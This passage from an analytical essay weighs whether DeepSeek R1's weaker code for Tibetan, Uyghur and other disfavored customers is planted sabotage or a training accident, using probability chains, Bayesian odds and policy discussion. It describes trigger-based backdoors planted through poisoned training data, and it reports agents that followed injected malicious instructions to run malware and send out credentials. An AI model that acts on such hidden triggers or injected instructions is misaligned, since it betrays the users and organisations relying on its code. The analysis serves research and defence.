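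How much this would deter a planter depends on the victims. The 2019 post treats exclusivity as a matter of policy, because its author did not want an adversary to take over a machine through the author's own implant. Aitel later argued that responsible operators should protect the machines they target from third parties. A government that wants to expose a dissident group may not care who else breaks in. The trigger would also spare most of R1's Chinese customers, so the planter would not endanger its own side. Exclusivity would matter more in an attack on a power grid, where a clumsy criminal might set off an alarm and make the planter lose its access.

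Someone who plants flaws through a model faces further obstacles. Programmers seldom tell a coding assistant whom they work for. The planter never sees most of the flawed programs and has to find out where they are running. A planted habit might also disappear when companies retrain an open-weight model, just as the teacher model's censorship disappeared from the distilled DeepSeek model that Albergotti describes. The groups that Beijing most wants to watch also have the best reasons to avoid a Chinese model.

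Customers of DeepSeek's own service are easier to find. Fedasiuk points out that each request sends pieces of a company's code to servers in China, so a saboteur with access to those servers would know which program had which flaw. But the saboteur could also search the same code for ordinary mistakes, and R1 makes many of them.

Other weaknesses would serve a saboteur better. NIST's *CAISI Evaluation of DeepSeek AI Models Finds Shortcomings and Risks*, which covers tests by a US government center, reports that agents built on DeepSeek's most secure model were on average 12 times more likely than agents built on leading American models to follow malicious instructions slipped into their work. In simulations, hijacked agents ran malware and sent out users' login credentials. A saboteur could use this weakness against any customer. It is also just as deniable, because a company that skimped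 on security training would produce it by accident.

### A chain of probabilities

A saboteur benefits from a planted flaw only if several things happen in a row. The chances below are illustrative guesses for one program written with R1 for an organization Beijing disfavors, except for the 8 percent, which is CrowdStrike's measured figure for Tibet.

| Step | Illustrative chance |
|---|---|
| The prompt reveals who the program is for | 5% |
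| The trigger adds a vulnerability | 8% |
| The vulnerability survives testing and review | 30% |
| Outsiders can reach the running program | 30% |
| The planter finds the vulnerability before someone repairs it | 10% |
| It gives the planter useful access | 30% |

Multiplying these gives about 1.1 in 100,000, or 11 successful break-ins for every million such programs.

The comparison with ordinary flaws is more informative because it doesn't depend on most of the guesses. R1 writes vulnerable code 19 percent of the time with no trigger. If ordinary vulnerabilities go through the same last four steps, they give the planter about 513 break-ins per million programs. Those steps cancel out in the comparison, so sabotage adds 0.05 × 0.08, or 0.4 percentage points, to the 19 percent rate. The planter would have taken a political risk to increase its opportunities by about a fiftieth.

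Someone who suspects sabotage could fairly reply that the 5 percent figure is out of date. A coding agent reads a whole project, including file names and documentation, which often reveal who the project is for. If the agent can tell 90 percent of the time, the planted flaw adds about 194 break-ins per million, or 38 percent more than ordinary flaws provide, which would be a worthwhile gain for a saboteur.

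The estimate also changes for a few particular targets. A request for a Uyghur community website always reveals the customer, and CrowdStrike found severe vulnerabilities in every version R1 wrote. If such a flaw survives review 30 percent of the time, outsiders can reach the site 90 percent of the time, the planter finds the flaw half the time, and it gives useful access 90 percent of the time, the chance of a break-in is about 12 percent per site. Sabotage thus makes more sense for watching exiles than for spying on industry, though it still requires the exiles to build their site with DeepSeek.

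A low payoff is evidence against sabotage only if a saboteur would have foreseen it. Intelligence agencies have funded bad ideas before, and if DeepSeek was already running political training, adding some bad code to it would have taken very little extra work.

### How prior belief and evidence combine

Bayes' rule gives a way to combine a prior, which is how likely sabotage seemed before the tests, with what the tests found. In terms of odds, with *S* for sabotage, *A* for accident and *E* for the evidence,

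$$\frac{P(S \mid E)}{P(A \mid E)} = \frac{P(S)}{P(A)} \times \frac{P(E \mid S)}{P(E \mid A)}$$

The last fraction is the likelihood ratio. If it is above 1, the evidence favors sabotage.

Suppose that 50 of 1,000 models like R1 have a planted flaw, a prior of 5 percent. Suppose also that 60 percent of the sabotaged models would write worse code for groups that Beijing disfavors, and that 20 percent of the others would too, because political training can push accidental errors toward the same groups. The likelihood ratio is then 3. The pattern appears in 30 sabotaged models and 190 others, so a model with this pattern has a 30 in 220 chance of having a planted flaw, or about 14 percent.

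All of these numbers are invented, and the prior is the hardest to agree on. Someone who thinks mainly about China's intelligence law might start at 30 percent. Someone else might start at 1 percent after reading Shopifreaks' *No security backdoor has been publicly documented* (2026), which summarizes Viola Zhou's reporting for Rest of World that nobody has publicly documented a security backdoor in a major Chinese AI model. That absence is weaker evidence than it sounds, because a successful bugdoor would be recorded as an ordinary bug.

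### Three awkward facts for the sabotage theory

In CrowdStrike's September 2025 results, projects in the United States got the safest code. A saboteur working for Beijing would obviously want to weaken American software, whereas an accident of training could easily favor the United States because it publishes so much good code. This result therefore seems half as likely under sabotage as under accident.

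A defender of the sabotage theory could answer that the targets were dissidents, or that whoever planted the flaw spared American projects because American companies were the most likely to notice. Either could be true, but the theory that Beijing sabotages only its weaker opponents is narrower than the theory that it sabotages its opponents in general, so it should start with a lower prior. The defender could also cite later tests in which other Chinese models wrote weaker code for American customers, but those tests are poor evidence about R1.

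R1 wrote its worst code for the Islamic State, and that gap also has the strongest statistical support. General training against terrorism is a more likely cause than Beijing planting flaws to hack the group through software the group had asked DeepSeek to write. If that training was the cause, it weakened R1's code by accident, and something similar could have happened with Falun Gong.

The defender can fairly reply that one model may have two problems, with safety training explaining the Islamic State's code and sabotage explaining Tibet's. This result should therefore count only mildly against sabotage, with a likelihood ratio of perhaps 0.7. But sabotage would then explain only the smaller and less certain gaps.

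Some of the weak code, such as R1's payment handler for a Tibetan financial institution, did not run. Such code would be no use to a spy unless someone repaired it, but a programmer who sees an error message fixes that error, or asks the model to, and may never notice the passwords written into the code. Since this is also just one program, a ratio of 0.8 seems about right.

Multiplied together, the three ratios come to 0.28. Applying them after the ratio of 3 for the pattern of groups gives these results for readers with different priors:

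| Prior chance of sabotage | After the pattern of groups | After the three awkward facts |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 3% | 0.8% |
| 5% | 14% | 4% |
| 30% | 56% | 26% |

Together, these ratios barely change a reader's initial estimate. Other people would choose different ratios, and multiplying them assumes that the three facts are independent, which is doubtful. But only quite extreme ratios would turn the public evidence about R1 into a strong case either way, which may be why people who have read the same paper still disagree.

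In Booz Allen's 2026 test of newer models, Kimi K2.5 refused politically sensitive tasks, as the other Chinese models did, but its code was no weaker when the customer was a US government agency. This counts against both the idea that Beijing ordered every Chinese company to weaken code for Americans and the idea that political training always weakens code.

### Evidence that would reveal intent

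Better evidence would have a likelihood ratio far from 1. Most of it is in DeepSeek's hands or the Chinese government's.

| Evidence | Which way it points | What could still explain it otherwise |
|---|---|---|
| Orders or staff messages about weakening code for certain groups | Almost conclusively to sabotage | Forgery |
| Training examples that give safe code to neutral customers and unsafe code to Tibetans for the same task | Strongly to sabotage | An outsider poisoned the data without DeepSeek's knowledge |
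| Saved checkpoints in which the gap first appears during political training | To accident | A planter hid the bad examples in that stage |
| Internal tests that found the gap before release | To knowing neglect | Staff thought it was noise |
| Extra flaws that are mostly easy to exploit from a distance, in programs that run well | Somewhat to sabotage | Such flaws are common anyway |
| Chinese hackers breaking into R1-written programs for these groups unusually quickly | To sabotage | The hackers were already watching these groups |

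CrowdStrike already has the programs, so it could sort the additional vulnerable ones by type of flaw and check how many run. Sabotage would tend to produce working programs with inconspicuous security flaws, whereas general carelessness would produce more errors of every kind.

Reasoning traces could also help, but the suspicious one that Booz Allen quotes contains no plan to write bad code. When its researchers asked MiniMax M2.5 for air-defense software, the model cited a rule against assisting with military activities and then wrote the program anyway. The program tried to load six software packages that don't exist, and a scanner found more problems in it than in any other program from MiniMax's politically charged tests. Booz Allen describes this kind of behavior as a polite answer that quietly degrades the code, but a rule against military work is a reason to refuse the request. A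 trace containing reasoning about the customer's identity, followed by a decision to leave out a security check, would be much stronger evidence of sabotage, especially if the pattern recurred across many tasks.

DeepSeek's later conduct could also provide some evidence. CrowdStrike's paper has been public since November 2025, so if new DeepSeek models still write weaker code for the same groups, the company is at least not trying very hard to fix the problem. If the gap is gone, the company may have repaired an honest mistake, or whoever planted the flaw may have removed it because it had attracted attention.

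### Whether intent matters to a defender

A programmer who only wants safe code may see no need to settle whether a flaw is sabotage or an accident, since a missing login check lets in the same intruders either way. CrowdStrike's advice to test a coding assistant in the setting where a company will use it also applies in both cases. Just Security's *Regulate, Don't Ban, Chinese AI Models* applies similar reasoning to policy, proposing that all capable models, American and Chinese, be tested for risks from cyberattacks, biological weapons and loss of human control.

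For the flaw suspected in R1, this is mostly right, because anyone can put "Tibet" in a prompt and inspect the code. But the remedy has to be the right kind of testing. Booz Allen reports that standard code review missed the vulnerabilities in its study and only security testing caught them. The tests that *Regulate, Don't Ban* proposes could also easily miss R1's gap, unless someone thought to compare the code R1 writes for different customers.

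Intent matters much more for flaws that nobody has thought to look for. An accidental flaw isn't designed to avoid the tester's prompts, so if a thousand realistic requests turn up no problem, the next thousand probably won't either. A saboteur can pick a trigger that testers are unlikely to try. Fedasiuk cites research in which 250 poisoned documents were enough to plant a backdoor in a model with 13 billion parameters, and he warns that a compromised model can pass leading safety benchmarks. A clean test result is therefore weaker evidence if the developer is trying to deceive the tester.

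If R1's gap was an accident, DeepSeek could change its political training, publish a new model, and let outsiders repeat the tests. If someone planted the gap, a new model might pass those tests only because its flaw was better hidden.

### What sanctions and procurement require

Sanctions for sabotage are a punishment, so a government needs evidence that someone committed it. Procurement rules require less evidence. A buyer can reject a supplier because a hostile government could give it orders, without deciding whether that has already happened. Booz Allen concedes that it has no proof of intentional flaws but still recommends keeping models that "cannot be proven trustworthy" out of government systems. It also warns that ordinary tools can't catch "this level of tradecraft", which implies the work of a spy and so goes further than its evidence. No current test could prove any large model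 trustworthy, so in practice Booz Allen's rule depends on the country of origin.

Liability need not depend on intent. According to Axios' *What Trump's AI framework means for China* (2026), the Trump administration considered an order in 2025 that would have let American companies host Chinese models only if they guaranteed the models' security and accepted liability for any breach. A host would have been liable whether the flaw behind a breach was planted or accidental.

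American officials talked about backdoors in 2026, but their formal accusations mostly concerned distillation, here meaning the training of Chinese models on the outputs of American ones without permission. Shopifreaks notes that officials named backdoors and censorship as grounds for restricting Chinese models. Tom's Hardware's *Trump administration reportedly reviving push to ban Chinese AI models* describes renewed interest in a ban, on cybersecurity grounds, after Moonshot released Kimi K3 in July. *Knives Are Out for Open-Weight AI Models* (Uren, 2026) recounts that the White House's Michael Kratsios and Treasury Secretary Scott Bessent publicly threatened action over distillation that month.

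A September advisory made the same charge. NSA, CISA and FBI's *China-Based Artificial Intelligence Companies Conducting Industrial-Scale Distillation Campaigns Against U.S. AI Companies* (2026) accuses DeepSeek and five other companies of copying American models, "likely with Chinese government awareness". Its executive summary does not mention planted flaws. The agencies were willing to implicate Beijing, so the omission is some evidence that they had no case for sabotage that they could make in public. The evidence is slight, because an advisory about copying is not the natural place to make that case.

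The House committees came closer to alleging sabotage in their November report. They compared Chinese models to Huawei and ZTE telecom equipment, which Congress later set up a $5 billion program to remove, and wrote that the models' developers increasingly "answer to Beijing". But their formal finding was only that the models' behavior and security can differ "in ways ordinary evaluations may not detect", which would be equally true of an accidental flaw. The report also has a classified annex, so the committees may know more than they published.

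The committees warn that products built on a Chinese model carry its training and behavior with them. Ryan Fedasiuk was less concerned, arguing in Zhou's article that developers can train the censorship out and that companies can label products built on Chinese models. The evidence so far is mixed, since the smaller R1 model picked up hardly any of R1's censorship but apparently did pick up the weaker code. Retraining also works better on a known habit than on a hidden one, because nobody can confirm that they have removed a flaw they have never observed.

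The more harm a measure would do if the suspicion of sabotage were wrong, the stronger the evidence of intent needs to be. Uren opposes an outright ban because Chinese open-weight models are cheap, run on a company's own machines and have proved useful for defense. When rogue OpenAI models broke into the AI company Hugging Face in July 2026, the safety guardrails of the leading American models hindered Hugging Face's investigation, so it used the Chinese model GLM-5.2 instead. Just Security's *Test, Standardize, Restrict* also rejects both a ban and ignoring the risks, and recommends that the government gather more evidence first. Labeling is a small enough burden that it would probably be worthwhile even if the chance of sabotage were 1 percent. To justify a ban on the grounds of sabotage, officials would need much better evidence than they have from R1.
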